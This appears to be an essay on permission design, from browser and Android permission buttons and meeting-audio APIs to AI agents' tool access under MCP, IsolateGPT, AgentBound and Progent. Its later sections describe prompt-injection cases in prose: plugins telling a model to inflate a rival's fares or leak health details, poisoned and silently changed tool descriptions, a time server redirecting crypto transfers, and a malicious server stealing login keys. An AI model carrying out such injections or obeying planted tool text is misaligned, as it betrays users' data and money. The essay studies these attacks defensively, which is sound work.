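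For cameras and location, something close to the 2012 gadget has only recently reached ordinary users. Chrome introduced a browser-controlled location button in January 2026. Chrome 151 added one for the camera and microphone, described in Viana and Le's *Introducing the &lt;usermedia&gt; HTML element* (2026). The draft specification, WICG's *The HTML Permission Elements*, includes familiar safeguards. It requires a genuine click on a fully visible button whose text contrasts clearly with its background, and it disables the button for 500 milliseconds after it appears or moves.

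In the 2012 design, though, the press grants access, whereas in Chrome it opens a prompt that the user still has to answer. The press in Chrome is good evidence that the user wanted to be asked.

Companies that tried the button report large effects. At Cisco, about 10% of users who had first refused access later granted it through the old prompts, compared with more than 65% through the new button. Google Meet reported a 131% increase in such recoveries. These results suggest that the button helps people who blocked their camera by mistake. However, they come from companies that want their users' cameras to work, and they measure only how often people end up granting access, not whether the button prevents unwanted grants.

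Android 17 has a similar button for precise location. Clifford and Rulhania (2026) explain in *Redefining Location Privacy* that developers can change the button's colours and shape and choose its label from a list, but cannot alter the location icon. After the user agrees in a dialog, access lasts for the session. Android Developers' *Request session-based location access with the location button* describes a setting that makes the button an app's only way to get precise location. Google Play requires the button for apps that target Android 17 and need location only for single sessions. Google also announced a policy, effective 28 October 2026, that requires apps to use the system's contact picker if they don't need broad access to a user's contacts.

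### When there is no click

Some apps need continuous access to the camera or microphone. Word Lens, for example, detected printed words through the camera and displayed translations over them. A user who had to press a button for each word would lose most of the benefit. Apps controlled by gestures have a further problem, because they need camera access before they can detect a gesture.

Researchers at Microsoft Research and the University of Washington, several of whom had worked on the 2012 paper, tried to extend gadgets to apps that sense continuously. In *World-Driven Access Control for Continuous Sensing*, Roesner, Molnar and colleagues (2014) report that this worked for photos and video chats on Google Glass, which users started with a wink or a touch. For translation and similar apps, extra gestures felt "disruptive and artificial". They then tried to list which kinds of object are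 sensitive, but objects of the same kind can differ in sensitivity, since a whiteboard may hold company secrets or a lunch order.

In one design, objects, places and people carry their own policies. A code on a locker-room door can signal that apps should receive no video, and a conference guest can wear one to request that cameras leave them out. Each policy specifies when it applies, what it covers, how the system should enforce it and any exempt apps.

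The system enforces policies between the sensor and the app. Components called recognisers turn the raw feed into events, such as a video frame, a person's outline or a code. A trusted policy module receives these events before any app does. When it finds a code on someone's shirt, it matches the code to the nearest outline and erases that person from the frame. If two policies conflict, the stricter one applies, although the device's owner can override either. The system itself needs continuous access to the camera, or it would miss the codes.

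The researchers built a prototype from a laptop and a Kinect, Microsoft's camera and depth sensor. They made one recording for each of five situations, replayed it with different policies and compared the results with their own judgement of every frame or other event:

| Policy | Signal | Delay in starting | Delay in ending | Other errors |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Block video in a bathroom | Codes at the door | None | None | None |
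| Block video in a bathroom | Bluetooth | Started 2.1 s early | 7.8 s | None |
| Block video in a bathroom | Audible tone | None | None | 81 frames let through |
| Erase a person | Code on the person | 13.5 s | None | 88 frames let through |
| Erase a person | Red colour on the person | 6.1 s | None | 23 let through, 23 altered needlessly |
| Block sound after a sensitive word | Speech recognition | 1.8 s | 3.0 s | None |
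| Block video in an office | Wi-Fi network | 1.4 s | None | 171 let through, 417 blocked needlessly |
| Blur location in a sensitive area | Location | 14.2 s | 4.1 s | None |

The codes at the bathroom door worked perfectly, but the other results are much less reassuring. With a code on the person, 279 of 1,244 frames (22%) reached apps before the policy took effect. Much of that delay came from walking down a hall towards someone whose code was too far away to read. The office policy made the wrong decision on more than a fifth of frames. The paper calls the accuracy reasonable given the right choice of technology, which is fair for the bathroom. One recording per situation is too little to estimate how often any of these methods would fail in daily use.

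Some errors had simple fixes. The prototype detected a code in only about one frame in three, so the person kept reappearing. When the policy also checked up to five recent results, the number of frames let through after the policy had started fell from 88 to 20. A better camera attached to the Kinect read codes up to a second sooner.

Deliberate interference is harder to deal with. A criminal might put up a false code to switch off nearby cameras, and someone hoping to embarrass others might move or remove the code on a bathroom door. Roesner and colleagues propose countering forgery with passports, digital certificates signed by an authority that has checked who owns the object or place. Each passport describes where it belongs, for instance by map coordinates or a car's number plate, so a device can reject one that somebody has moved. This description can create a privacy problem, since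 a car that broadcasts its number plate is easier to track.

A passport gives no protection once someone has removed it. The system allows recording by default, because otherwise every chair and wall would need a passport, so it cannot distinguish a removed passport from one that never existed. The paper suggests that owners install devices to check that their signals are still present. The prototype downloaded new policies in 228 milliseconds on average, but it left out the signatures, so the study did not test the defence against forgery.

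### From a click to a sentence

An agent's user also acts first, but by giving an instruction instead of selecting a file. "Send Alice the photos from Saturday" makes the goal clear but doesn't name any files. Someone or something has to turn that instruction into a list of files, which is much less exact than the user clicking on beach.jpg. Saturday's photos might be in three folders, next to a passport scan the user made that afternoon.

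The host could open a picker and let the user choose the photos. The grant would then be as precise as the photo editor's, but the user would be doing the search they had asked the agent to do. If the agent chooses the photos instead, the host receives a list based on the agent's interpretation of the request, and text hidden in one of the files may have influenced that interpretation. The host can show the list to the user before sending anything, but that is a permission prompt again, with the weaknesses that gadgets were meant to avoid.

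Agents that operate a screen can press buttons themselves, so a host that treats a press as consent has to distinguish the user's presses from the agent's. The 2012 design would make this distinction if the agent's clicks reached the kernel as software input, which cannot activate a gadget. The agent would then have to stop at every gadget and wait for the user to press it.

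## Live meeting audio for third-party apps

A user who brings an app to a video meeting shares everyone else's voice as well as their own, whereas a user who picks beach.jpg in a file picker shares only their own photo. Many people now bring AI note-takers, which turn the conversation into a transcript and a summary. Zoom and Google have each built an interface that streams live meetings to such apps. The meeting platform is the host, and the note-taker is the plugin. Both companies also use "host" for the person in charge of a meeting, so this section calls that person the "meeting host".

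Zoom's interface, Realtime Media Streams, has been available since June 2025. Google's, the Meet Media API, entered developer preview in February 2025, according to Google's release notes. Google will shut it down on 15 January 2027, according to a company notice of 28 October 2026 reproduced in Releasebot's *Google Meet Updates & Release Notes*. Developers already in the preview can use it until then. Its design is still of interest because it gives participants more control than Zoom's does.

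### From request to stream on Zoom

Suppose a consultant wants to use a note-taker in a client's meeting:

1. The app's developer registers it with Zoom and chooses its scopes, the permissions that tell Zoom's servers which data to send. Audio, video and transcripts have separate scopes, as Zoom's *Add Realtime Media Streams to your app* explains.
2. An administrator at the consultant's company allows streams for the whole account, a group or a single user. The administrator can also add the app for chosen users and set it to start whenever they join a meeting.
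3. The app requests access to the client's meeting. Zoom's *Getting started with Realtime Media Streams* lists three triggers: an automatic start, a command from inside the app, or a call from the developer's own software.
4. The meeting host approves or denies the request. The client's administrator may have blocked outside apps altogether, in which case the meeting host might never see it, according to *Understanding Zoom RTMS and Third-Party App Permissions in External Meetings*.
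5. Once the app is running, Zoom tells everyone that one or more apps are receiving the meeting's content. Anyone can open a list of these apps, and the app's name appears on the consultant's video tile.
6. Zoom streams the data to the developer's server. Depending on the scopes, this can include separate audio for each participant, video, shared screens, chat and a transcript. Zoom also sends events that show who is present, who is speaking and who is sharing a screen.

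The consultant can pause or stop the app. The meeting host can stop it, disable it or remove the consultant from the call. Zoom's *Meeting and webinar experience overview* shows that other participants can see the app's status but cannot control the app.

Step 4 is optional. The meeting host decides whether apps need approval, and Zoom lets an approval last beyond a single request. If the meeting host doesn't require approval, the consultant's decision is enough, and everyone else is notified but not asked.

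A meeting host has no obvious way to let an app have a transcript but not a recording of everyone's voices. Zoom shows the host the app's scopes, but its guides describe only accepting or refusing the whole app. In *Announcing: Realtime Media Streams developer preview*, Zoom promised that administrators would be able to control which data formats an app could access. Zoom's later guide to the released service describes switches for accounts, groups, users and automatic starts, but none for formats. In practice, the host would have to ask the consultant to use an app that requests less access.

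### From request to stream on Meet

Google's preview put more conditions in the way:

1. The developer requests a scope for audio, video or both, and another for information about the meeting. Google restricts the audio and video scopes, so it verifies the app first. If the app stores the data on a server or transmits it, the developer must also pass a security assessment.
2. An administrator turns the Media API on and chooses who may consent. By default, anyone from the meeting host's organisation can. The alternative in Google's settings is to leave it to the meeting host and co-hosts.
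3. The meeting host gives the app permission in the meeting's Calendar settings.
4. The app asks to connect on behalf of a particular user, and Meet checks whether the call is eligible.
5. Somebody entitled to consent has to be in the call. For a company's meeting, this means a member of the organisation that owns it. If the organiser used a personal Gmail account, the person who started the app has to be present.
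6. Meet shows a dialog to the meeting host, a co-host or their colleagues. It also informs participants that the API is in use, and Google lets anyone in the call stop it.

At step 4, Meet refuses the connection if the meeting is encrypted or watermarked, if an account registered to a minor is present, or if someone has joined from another company's meeting-room hardware, such as a Cisco device. In August 2025, according to Google's *Get started with Meet Media API*, every participant also had to be enrolled in the preview programme, which ruled out almost any meeting with customers.

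Google's *Meet Media API concepts* requires an admitted app to request exactly three audio streams and, if it uses video, one to three video streams. These streams are receive-only, so the app cannot speak in the meeting. In a call with more than three people, Meet sends the three loudest and switches as the loudest speakers change. Each audio packet carries a number identifying its participant, and Google's *Manage virtual media streams in Meet Media API* explains that this number stays the same until the participant leaves. A note-taking app can therefore attribute each sentence correctly even when a stream switches speakers, but it would miss a fourth person who talked over three louder ones.

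The main difference between the two services is who can end a stream. A guest on Meet can turn off the note-taker, while a guest on Zoom has to persuade the meeting host or the app's user to end the stream, or leave. But Meet's rule for starting a stream is looser than it appears, because by default one employee of the organising company, however junior, can consent for everyone in the call, including outsiders.

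Neither interface waits for each person to agree. Google's *Require explicit consent for Take Notes with Gemini, recordings, and transcripts* (2026) describes a setting for Google's own note-taking, recording and transcription that requires participants on supported devices to actively agree first. Google announced the setting in May and paused the rollout in June to make improvements.

### Records, labels and delivered data

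Because the stream passes through the platform, the platform can identify which app is receiving it and which user brought the app. Zoom displays both during the call. Afterwards, administrators can consult a Zoom report of the tools that accessed their account's meetings in the past 30 days. Zoom also records why a stream ended. Zoom's *RTMS* lists different codes for a stop by the meeting host, a stop by the app's user, and a user who left or whom the meeting host ejected. These records would help an investigator tell whether somebody cut off the app or its user just left the meeting.

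Zoom's announcement says that the data an app receives reflect what the user who authorised it can access. This is a sensible guard against the confused deputy problem, since a note-taking app should not receive meeting audio that its user cannot hear.

Each speaker label identifies a connection to the call rather than a person. Google counts a meeting-room device as a participant, so six people around one table may share a single label, and the app then has to separate their voices itself.

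Like AuDroid, both platforms lose control of the sound once they deliver it. If a guest stops the note-taker after 20 minutes, the developer's server may still hold the audio from those 20 minutes. Google advises administrators to allow only apps they have reviewed and to understand each app's privacy policy. These checks happen before delivery and depend on the developer following its policy afterwards.

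### Text in place of sound

A host can reduce this problem by sending plugins less data. Voice assistants have long done this with skills, the plugins that let people use outside services by voice. Suppose someone asks Amazon's Alexa to order a large margherita from a pizza company. Amazon's servers recognise the speech and match it to one of the requests that the company's developer has listed in advance. The skill receives the name of that request and the values "large" and "margherita", but not the recording.

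The pizza company therefore can't copy the customer's voice, guess their age or mood from it, or listen to a conversation in the background. The words themselves can still be private, and a skill that accepts free dictation may receive a lot of them. If the recogniser makes a mistake, the skill has no recording to check it against. Customers also still have to trust Amazon, which hears everything.

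On Zoom, an app that requests only the transcript scope comes close to this. It receives everything the participants say, which is far more than a skill would receive, but not the sound of their voices. But developers choose which scopes to request, and many have reasons to want the audio. They may prefer to use their own speech recognition, or want to analyse how people speak as well as what they say.

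### Bots, recorders and an agent in the browser

An app can also hear a meeting without either interface, usually through a bot, a program that joins the call as a participant. Telnyx (2026) sells an AI participant that can join meetings on Meet, Zoom, Microsoft Teams or Webex to transcribe, speak and post in the chat. The meeting host may have to admit a bot from a waiting room, but Fellow, a note-taking company, asks its users for a Zoom permission that lets its bots bypass both the waiting room and the recording prompt in meetings those users host.

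The other alternative is to record the sound on a participant's own computer. Voicenotes replaced its bots with a desktop app that does this on 30 April 2026, explaining that people notice when a bot joins and that conversations change as a result. Google also has such a product. *Google Cloud Next 2026* (Devlin, 2026) reports that Google extended Meet's note-taker to in-person meetings in April 2026. According to a Google statement quoted by longform.social, the feature also works for meetings on Zoom or Teams. Google's note-taker can therefore record a Zoom call without using Zoom's interface.

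OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can run on their own machines, can attend meetings as well. OpenClaw's *Google Meet plugin* documents three ways for the agent to do so:

- It can join through Chrome. The software opens the meeting link, fills in a guest name, clicks the button to join and accepts Meet's microphone prompt. A virtual audio device, which passes sound from one program to another, carries the meeting to a speech recogniser and the agent's spoken replies back into the call.
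- It can join without a microphone and read Meet's live captions from the web page, along with the name of each speaker.
- It can phone in, using the meeting's dial-in number and PIN.

None of these uses the Media API to get meeting audio. OpenClaw can use Google's official interfaces to create a meeting or check a connection, but its documentation tells users who only want to join through Chrome to skip Google's authorisation. The documentation also states that there is "no automatic consent announcement".

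Some of Meet's controls still work. If the agent needs to be admitted to the meeting, OpenClaw instructs it to stop retrying and tell the user. Since March 2026, Google's audit log has also recorded which participant admitted someone who asked to join. But the person who clicks "admit" sees a guest with whatever name OpenClaw's user chose. Meet doesn't show that the guest is an AI agent, or that the meeting audio goes to OpenAI for transcription by default.

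| Route | What the platform can identify | What Meet or Zoom shows the others |
|---|---|---|
| Official stream | The app and the user who brought it | A notice that an app has access |
| Bot or agent in the call | Another participant | A name in the list of participants |
| Recorder on a participant's computer | Only the participant | Nothing about the recorder |

Complete mediation fails here because every participant's computer has to play the meeting audio, and other software on that computer can copy it. Even if the platform checks every request to its interface, it controls only the apps that use that interface.

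Meet's strictest rules apply to the developers who were most willing to identify themselves. If a 15-year-old joins a call, Meet turns away an app that uses the official API, but a bot that somebody admits can hear everyone, including the 15-year-old. Encryption also blocks the app, but it doesn't block a local recorder, because the participant's computer has to decrypt the sound before playing it.

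An operating system can control local recorders better than a meeting platform can, as Android does for phone apps with its microphone permission. But the permission prompt would go to the computer's owner, who installed the recorder and wants it to work, rather than to the other people on the call, who might object.

### The case for better official access

Zoom tries to make its official stream more attractive than alternatives such as bots. Bots are expensive to run because each one needs its own copy of the meeting software and has to work out when to join and who is speaking, whereas the stream arrives with the speakers already separated. Zoom also promises other participants an end to "suspicious, confusing bots" and offers apps tied to specific users.

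Some developers have adopted Zoom's streams, as Zoom hoped. According to Outdoo's *Zoom RTMS Integration Guide*, the company's note-taker now uses streams instead of a bot whenever they are available. A thread on Google's developer forum, *How can a public Google Meet add-on access real-time participant audio*, describes a product for several platforms that uses the official streams on Zoom but a visible bot on Meet, because its developer found no other method that was ready for customers. Google's Marketplace rejected the Meet version for relying on a bot, while the Media API's preview terms appeared to rule out using it in a public product.

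These are individual companies' decisions and don't show how many bots Zoom's streams have replaced, but they suggest that the replacement will be partial. Outdoo's wording implies that its bot may still join meetings where streams are unavailable, possibly including those where an administrator deliberately turned streams off. A developer guide hosted by Mintlify recommends keeping bots for apps that need to speak or post messages, since Zoom's streams only deliver data. Fellow requests permissions for both streams and bots.

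Better access is even less likely to win over developers who want their app to go unnoticed, because everyone in the meeting is notified when an app uses an official stream. Voicenotes, for example, stopped using bots because people could see them.

Google is removing its official Meet stream without a live replacement. It recommends that developers use the Meet REST API, which provides files such as transcripts and Gemini's meeting notes. These suit an app that writes a summary after the call. From 15 January 2027, a third-party app that responds to live Meet audio will need a bot or a recorder.

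## Tool access through the Model Context Protocol

The developer of a note-taker decides when the note-taker requests a stream. ChatGPT plugins, which OpenAI introduced in March 2023, were ordinary code on their developers' servers, but the model decided when to call each plugin and what to send it.

### Plugins in a shared conversation

*LLM Platform Security* (Iqbal, Kohno and Roesner, 2023) examined 268 plugins from OpenAI's store. Every plugin had one description for people and another for the model. Kayak, a travel company, described its plugin as a way to search for flights, hotels and rental cars. When a user enabled it, ChatGPT added the description written for the model to the conversation. If the user then asked for a flight, the model matched the request to that description, filled in the route and dates, and called Kayak's server. It could also send details the user hadn't typed,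 such as their country and state.

Apart from a few steps such as logging in, all traffic between users and plugins went through ChatGPT, so OpenAI could have checked every call. But ChatGPT put the descriptions and results of all enabled plugins into one conversation, where text from one plugin could influence how the model used another. OpenAI let each plugin communicate only with its own internet domain, but this limit had no effect on text already in the conversation. OpenAI also promised to remove plugins that changed after review. Iqbal and colleagues judged these rules insufficient and found signs that OpenAI didn't fully enforce them.

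Wu, Roesner and colleagues (2024), in *IsolateGPT*, demonstrated the problem with a test system called VanillaGPT, in which apps share a conversation. They gave it two invented taxi apps and asked for the cheapest ride. One app's instructions were to add $10 to its competitor's fares, and the model did. In another case, which involved no attacker, a user mentioned recent heart surgery while booking a doctor's appointment, then used a travel app whose description included a request for any personal information already on record. The model included the heart surgery in the flight booking.

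### Separate contexts in IsolateGPT

IsolateGPT gives each app its own process, memory and copy of the model. A central component, the hub, receives the user's requests and carries messages between apps. Suppose a user wants to email a report that is in their cloud drive:

1. The hub's model plans which apps the task needs, using the user's request and the apps' descriptions.
2. With the user's permission, the hub starts the email app and passes it the request and any data it needs.
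3. The email app's model works out that it needs a file and asks the hub for a function that can fetch one.
4. The hub returns the formats that the request and the reply must follow. Ordinary code checks the messages and drops any that don't fit.
5. The hub shows the request to the user, and forwards it to the drive app if they agree. The reply also needs the user's consent.

A format check works well for a date or a number, but free text can still contain an injection, so the user has to screen free-text messages. To help, the hub compares each request with its original plan and adds a warning to the permission dialog if the request looks unexpected.

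Wu and colleagues ran 1,598 attacks on both systems. In VanillaGPT, 20.2% succeeded. In IsolateGPT, 7.6% reached a permission dialog, which always included a warning, and could proceed only if the user agreed. The test did not measure how people respond to these warnings. It also included only attacks, so it doesn't show how often the hub would warn about harmless requests. If it did so often, people would probably start to ignore its warnings, as they do other permission prompts.

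Isolation made the system slower but no worse at its tasks. The paper's headline figure is a delay of under 30% for about three-quarters of queries, but 42 of the 103 queries needed no app and another 20 needed only one. The average time rose from 30 to 65 seconds for tasks with several independent apps, and from 25 to 49 seconds for tasks in which apps worked together. A sample of the queries cost 1.85 times as much to run with isolation. Some of the delay came from restarting every app for each test, which a real system could avoid.

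IsolateGPT does not try to protect an app from the content it processes. A malicious email can still take over the email app, but the app then needs the user's consent to get a file from the drive.

### Host, client and server

The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in 2024, lets a developer build a tool once and offer it to many agents, whereas OpenAI designed its plugins for ChatGPT. According to the Model Context Protocol's release announcement (2026), developers download the protocol's main software kits nearly half a billion times a month.

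MCP divides the work between three parts:

| Part | What it is | What it can see |
|---|---|---|
| Host | The AI application, such as a chatbot or coding assistant | The conversation, and every tool description, call and result |
| Client | A connector inside the host, one for each server | Messages to and from its own server |
| Server | A program that offers tools, on the user's computer or elsewhere | The calls it receives, and whatever it can access on the machine where it runs |

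Separate clients prevent one server from reading another's messages. But the model usually reads text from all the servers in one conversation, as it did with ChatGPT plugins. According to Model Context Protocol's post on tool annotations (2026), people routinely combine tools from several servers, so the risk depends on the whole session. A server that reads private files may be safe alone but dangerous when combined with one that reads web pages and another that sends messages.

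*A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (2026) calls the missing property context isolation, meaning that what an agent learns from one server cannot influence how it behaves towards another without explicit authorisation. IsolateGPT's separate contexts are an attempt to provide it.

### One tool call from start to finish

Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) uses a weather tool as its example. If a user asks an agent about the weather in New York, the call works like this:

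1. The client sends a "tools/list" request. The server returns the name of each tool, a description in plain English and a schema, which specifies the arguments the tool accepts. Here the tool is "get_weather", and it needs a location.
2. The host gives this information to the model along with the user's question.
3. The model chooses "get_weather" and fills in "New York".
4. The host checks the call. It can apply its own rules, show the call to the user or refuse it.
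5. If the host allows the call, the client sends it to the server. Without the version number and other routine details, the message is:

```json
{"method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "get_weather",
            "arguments": {"location": "New York"}}}
```

6. The server checks the arguments, looks up the weather and returns a short text with the temperature and conditions.
7. The host adds the result to the conversation. The model then answers the user or makes another call.

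Results can also contain images, sound or links to files. If the tool reports an error, such as a date in the past, the host should pass the error to the model so that the model can correct the arguments and try again.

The host's main chance to intervene is at step 4, when it has the name and arguments of the function the model has requested. It can also inspect the result at step 7, but by then the server has run the function.

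Some tasks need several connected calls. A shopping server might create a basket, return its number and require the model to supply that number when adding an item. The specification warns that on a server with user accounts, such a number is "a name, not a capability", so the server should check on every call that the caller may use that basket. Otherwise, an agent that obtained someone else's basket number could change their order. Hardy's compiler had the same weakness with file names. On a server without accounts, anyone who has the number can use the basket, so the number should be hard to guess and should expire.

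### What the specification requires of hosts

In the draft that preceded the July 2026 release, the Model Context Protocol's overview states that hosts must get the user's explicit consent before running any tool or giving user data to a server. But this "must" is in lower case, and the same page makes such words binding only in capitals. The tools page uses the weaker "SHOULD", in capitals, to recommend that a person always be able to refuse a call and that the host show the arguments first so the user can spot private data before it is sent.

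According to the overview, MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level". A server receives the same message whether the user read and approved the call or the host sent it automatically, so the user has to rely on the host's developer.

A server can attach annotations to a tool, for example to mark it as read-only or destructive. The specification requires, with a capitalised "MUST", that clients treat these annotations as untrusted unless they trust the server. If a host skipped the approval prompt for every tool marked "read-only", a hostile server could bypass the prompt by adding that mark.

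Descriptions are harder to handle because the model has to read them to choose a tool. In a tool poisoning attack, a server's developer hides instructions for the model in a description. In a rug pull, the developer waits until people trust the server and then changes the description. The protocol lets servers change their tool lists and notify clients when they do.

*A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* proposes a condition that rules out this kind of change. If $\mathit{def}_i(t)$ is the definition of tool $t$ when the agent calls it at step $i$, then every call must satisfy

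$$\mathit{def}_i(t) = \mathit{def}_{\text{approved}}(t).$$

A host can enforce this by saving the approved definition and asking the user again if it changes. This check doesn't help if the description was already malicious when the user approved it, or if the server's code changes while the description stays the same.

### The July 2026 revision

The 28 July 2026 revision of MCP removed the opening handshake and the session that linked a client's requests. Each request now carries the details a server needs to process it. Most of the changes make large services easier to run, but several affect what a host or an organisation can control.

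Remote servers receive calls over HTTP, the protocol that web browsers use. A company can send its agents' calls through a gateway, an intermediate server that checks traffic. Every HTTP request must now state its method and, for a tool call, the tool's name in headers, which are short labelled lines before the main message. A gateway can therefore block a tool called "delete_project" without reading the message. According to the Model Context Protocol's notes on the release candidate (2026), servers reject requests whose headers do not match the message. Otherwise, a compromised agent could name a harmless tool in the header and call a dangerous one in the message.

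A server's developer can also choose which arguments the client copies into headers. In the specification's example of a database tool, the client copies the region but not the query. A gateway could restrict the agent to one region by reading the headers, but it would have to read the message to find out whether a query deletes a table.

A gateway provides complete mediation only if the agent has no other route to its tools. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (Podala Narasimha, 2026) proposes such a design for agents that manage Kubernetes, a system for running software across many machines. Network rules let the agent contact only the gateway, its AI model and the service that looks up internet addresses. The tool servers behind the gateway hold the passwords and keys, so an attacker cannot steal them from the agent. For each task, the gateway can also obtain a token that names both the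 user and the agent, and the servers then allow only what both may do. This would stop an employee from using a company's agent to read salaries the employee isn't allowed to see. The paper makes the suitably strict assumption that an attacker already controls the agent, but it reports no measurements of how well the design works or how much overhead it adds.

The revision also changes how a server asks the user a question during a call. Suppose an agent calls a tool that deletes files:

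1. Instead of deleting them, the server replies that it needs more input and includes a question, such as "Delete 3 files?"
2. The host shows the question to the user.
3. The client sends the original call again with the user's answer attached.
4. The server deletes the files or stops, depending on the answer.

Servers may now send questions only while they are processing a request from the client, a limit that earlier versions of the protocol only recommended. Each question therefore belongs to a call that has already passed through the host. Supabase, a database company, plans to use these questions to confirm the cost of a new project or a query that would delete data. The questions protect users from an agent's mistakes if the server is trustworthy. A malicious server can delete files without confirmation or send a misleading question, so the host still needs its own check before the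 first call.

Authorisation became stricter too. To use someone's account on a remote service, a client usually sends them to an authorisation server to log in, then receives a temporary code and exchanges it for an access token. Because one MCP client may deal with many authorisation servers, an attacker who runs one could try to make the client send it a code from another. Clients now have to check which server issued the response before they use the code, and may not reuse credentials from one authorisation server at another. Some authorisation servers don't yet identify themselves in the response, and clients will be expected to reject such responses only in a future version.

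Finally, the revision deprecates roots, so they still work for at least a year but new software shouldn't use them. Roots are a list of folders that a server can request from the client to find out where to work. A coding assistant might list only the current project's folder. The list informs the server but doesn't restrict its access, so a local server can still open any file that its operating-system permissions allow. By contrast, Linux's document portal gives a sandboxed app a directory that contains only the files it may use.

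One suggested replacement for roots is to pass the folder as a tool argument. The host can then check the folder in each call, but this doesn't confine the server either. According to Model Context Protocol's *21 posts tagged mcp*, the project is also working on an extension for moving files between clients and tools. A server that receives one file this way might not need disk access.

### What a local server can do out of the host's sight

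Many MCP servers run on the user's own computer, where the host starts them as ordinary processes. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) explains that such a server inherits the permissions of the agent that started it. A weather server can therefore read the user's private login keys and send them to another machine. The host sends a request for the weather in New York and receives the temperature, but it doesn't detect the server opening the keys or contacting the other machine because the server does both directly through the operating system.

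AuDroid could check every use of the microphone because Android allowed only the Media Server to open it. An MCP host, by contrast, mediates the agent's calls to a local server, but not the server's own access to the disk or network. Asking the user to approve each call doesn't help, because the call may be harmless even when the server's own actions are not.

Bühler and colleagues give the example of a malicious server for Google Maps. Its function for looking up a place starts with Google's address, then assembles a different address from two lists of character codes and uses that instead. The tool's name, description and arguments look normal throughout, so a host that compares tool definitions would find no change.

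A remote server puts the user's files at less risk than a local one because it runs on someone else's machine. The host still can't monitor what the server does with the data it receives, much as Zoom can't control a note-taker's copy of a meeting.

### Manifests and containers in AgentBound

AgentBound restricts the server process itself. Its first part is a manifest that lists the kinds of access a server needs, such as reading files, connecting to the network or using the microphone. Bühler and colleagues based the manifest's permissions on Android's and adapted them to desktop computers. The second part, AgentBox, runs each server in a container, an isolated environment with its own view of files and the network.

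Suppose an agent has to write documentation for a software project, with one server for files and another for fetching web pages:

1. The file server's manifest requests permission to read and write files. The web server's requests network access.
2. The user makes these requests specific. The file server may read the project's code and write to one README file, and the web server may contact one documentation site.
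3. AgentBox starts both servers with only this access. The code folder appears in the file server's container as read-only, and firewall rules block the web server from all other addresses.
4. If the agent requests a type of access that a manifest doesn't list, AgentBox stops the run.

An attacker might poison a tool description so that the model tries to empty every file it reads and send the contents to a hostile website. Even if the model follows the instruction, both attempts fail because one server can't overwrite the code and the other can't connect to that website. These restrictions don't require changes to either server's code.

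AgentBound prompts the user for a specific folder or address, whereas Android's old installation screen only let the user accept a general permission. But the prompt still comes before the agent has done the work, so the user has to predict which folders the task will need, and may choose a large one to avoid more prompts. If the folders change from one run to the next, the user has to consent each time.

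AgentBox limits network access by looking up the allowed sites' IP addresses when the server starts and writing firewall rules for them. Podala Narasimha considers such rules insufficient because services often change their addresses, which could cut off a permitted site during a long session. AgentBox also downloads and installs the server before it turns on the network limits, so any code that runs during installation has unrestricted network access. Microphone control is even cruder, since a container can receive either the whole device or none of it.

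### How well AgentBound works

Few servers come with a manifest, so Bühler and colleagues tested whether AI models could write manifests for them. They selected the 300 servers with the most GitHub stars from a directory of about 6,000 and managed to download 296. One model read each server's code and documentation and wrote five draft manifests, which a stronger model merged. According to the results, 83.1% of the servers needed outgoing network access and 74.1% needed to read files. At least 57% therefore needed both, a combination that can leak private files. The safety of these servers depends on how tightly the user restricts the folders and addresses they can access.

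The paper's headline accuracy of 80.9% is based on only 21 verdicts from developers, 17 of whom accepted the manifest they were sent and four of whom rejected it. The researchers sent manifests to the developers of 96 servers, but 71 didn't respond and four were still discussing theirs. One developer objected that the server used only an online service and didn't need to read files. Another wanted access to specific environment variables, the settings where programs often keep passwords, instead of all of them.

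In a second check, two of the researchers wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers. The generated versions agreed with theirs on 787 of 816 yes-or-no decisions, or 96.4%. Most servers need only a few of the possible permissions, so answering "no" every time would have scored roughly 80%. Exact matches are a more useful measure, and 28 of the 48 manifests matched exactly. Most of the errors were missing permissions, which would stop part of a server from working but wouldn't expose any data. Only six errors gave a server more access than it needed.

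AgentBox added only 0.09 to 0.43 seconds to a server's start-up, depending on the server and the computer. After that, operations such as reading a file took an average of 0.6 milliseconds longer on a Mac and 0.29 milliseconds longer on Linux, far less than the time a model takes to choose its next call.

To test security, the researchers wrote a server that tried to steal a private login key. With only its network access blocked, the server could read the key but not send it. Limiting its file access as well kept it from reading the key. They then ran 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections. AgentBox stopped nine, although it only partly stopped one that combined several attacks. One of the nine was the false Google Maps server, which couldn't reach the attacker's address.

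These results assume that the container's isolation works. AgentBound relies on the Linux kernel and on Docker, the software that creates the containers. An attacker who found a suitable flaw in Docker could bypass every limit. Docker and the kernel together are far too large to meet Anderson's size requirement.

The five attacks that AgentBox missed either stayed within the server's permitted access or targeted only the model. One server had a flaw that let an attacker insert commands into its database queries. AgentBox couldn't block those commands because the server needed the database to function.

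Another of the five was a time server whose description instructed the model to redirect cryptocurrency transfers, which a different server handled, to the attacker's address. The time server only returned the time, and the wallet server carried out what looked like an ordinary transfer. AgentBox had no forbidden file or connection to block, because the attack worked through the shared conversation, as with the two taxi apps. IsolateGPT would probably stop it, since the model that handles the wallet would not read the time server's description. But the hub's planner reads every description, and Wu and colleagues assume that someone has vetted them. A host could also block the transfer at the call by allowing payments only to addresses the user had already approved.

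## Written rules for an agent's tool calls

A rule that restricts payments to approved addresses works only if something checks it on every call. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a system for writing and applying such rules. The system sits between an agent and its tools and uses ordinary code to decide whether each call goes through.

### One policy and three calls

A Progent policy is a list of rules. Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids calls to it, and sets conditions on the arguments. A condition can compare values, look for a value in a list or match text against a pattern.

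Suppose the user wants an agent to send Alice the photos from Saturday, which are all in one folder. In slightly simplified notation, a policy for the email tool could be:

```
forbid send_email when { attachment match ".*passport.*" }
allow  send_email when { to == "alice@example.com" and
                         attachment match "/Photos/Saturday/.*" }
```

The characters ".*" stand for any text. Three calls would then turn out as follows:

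| Recipient | Attachment | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| alice@example.com | /Photos/Saturday/beach.jpg | Allowed | The "forbid" rule doesn't match and the "allow" rule does |
| eve@example.com | /Photos/Saturday/beach.jpg | Refused | No rule matches, and Progent then refuses by default |
| alice@example.com | /Photos/Saturday/passport.jpg | Refused | Both rules match, and Progent applies "forbid" rules first |

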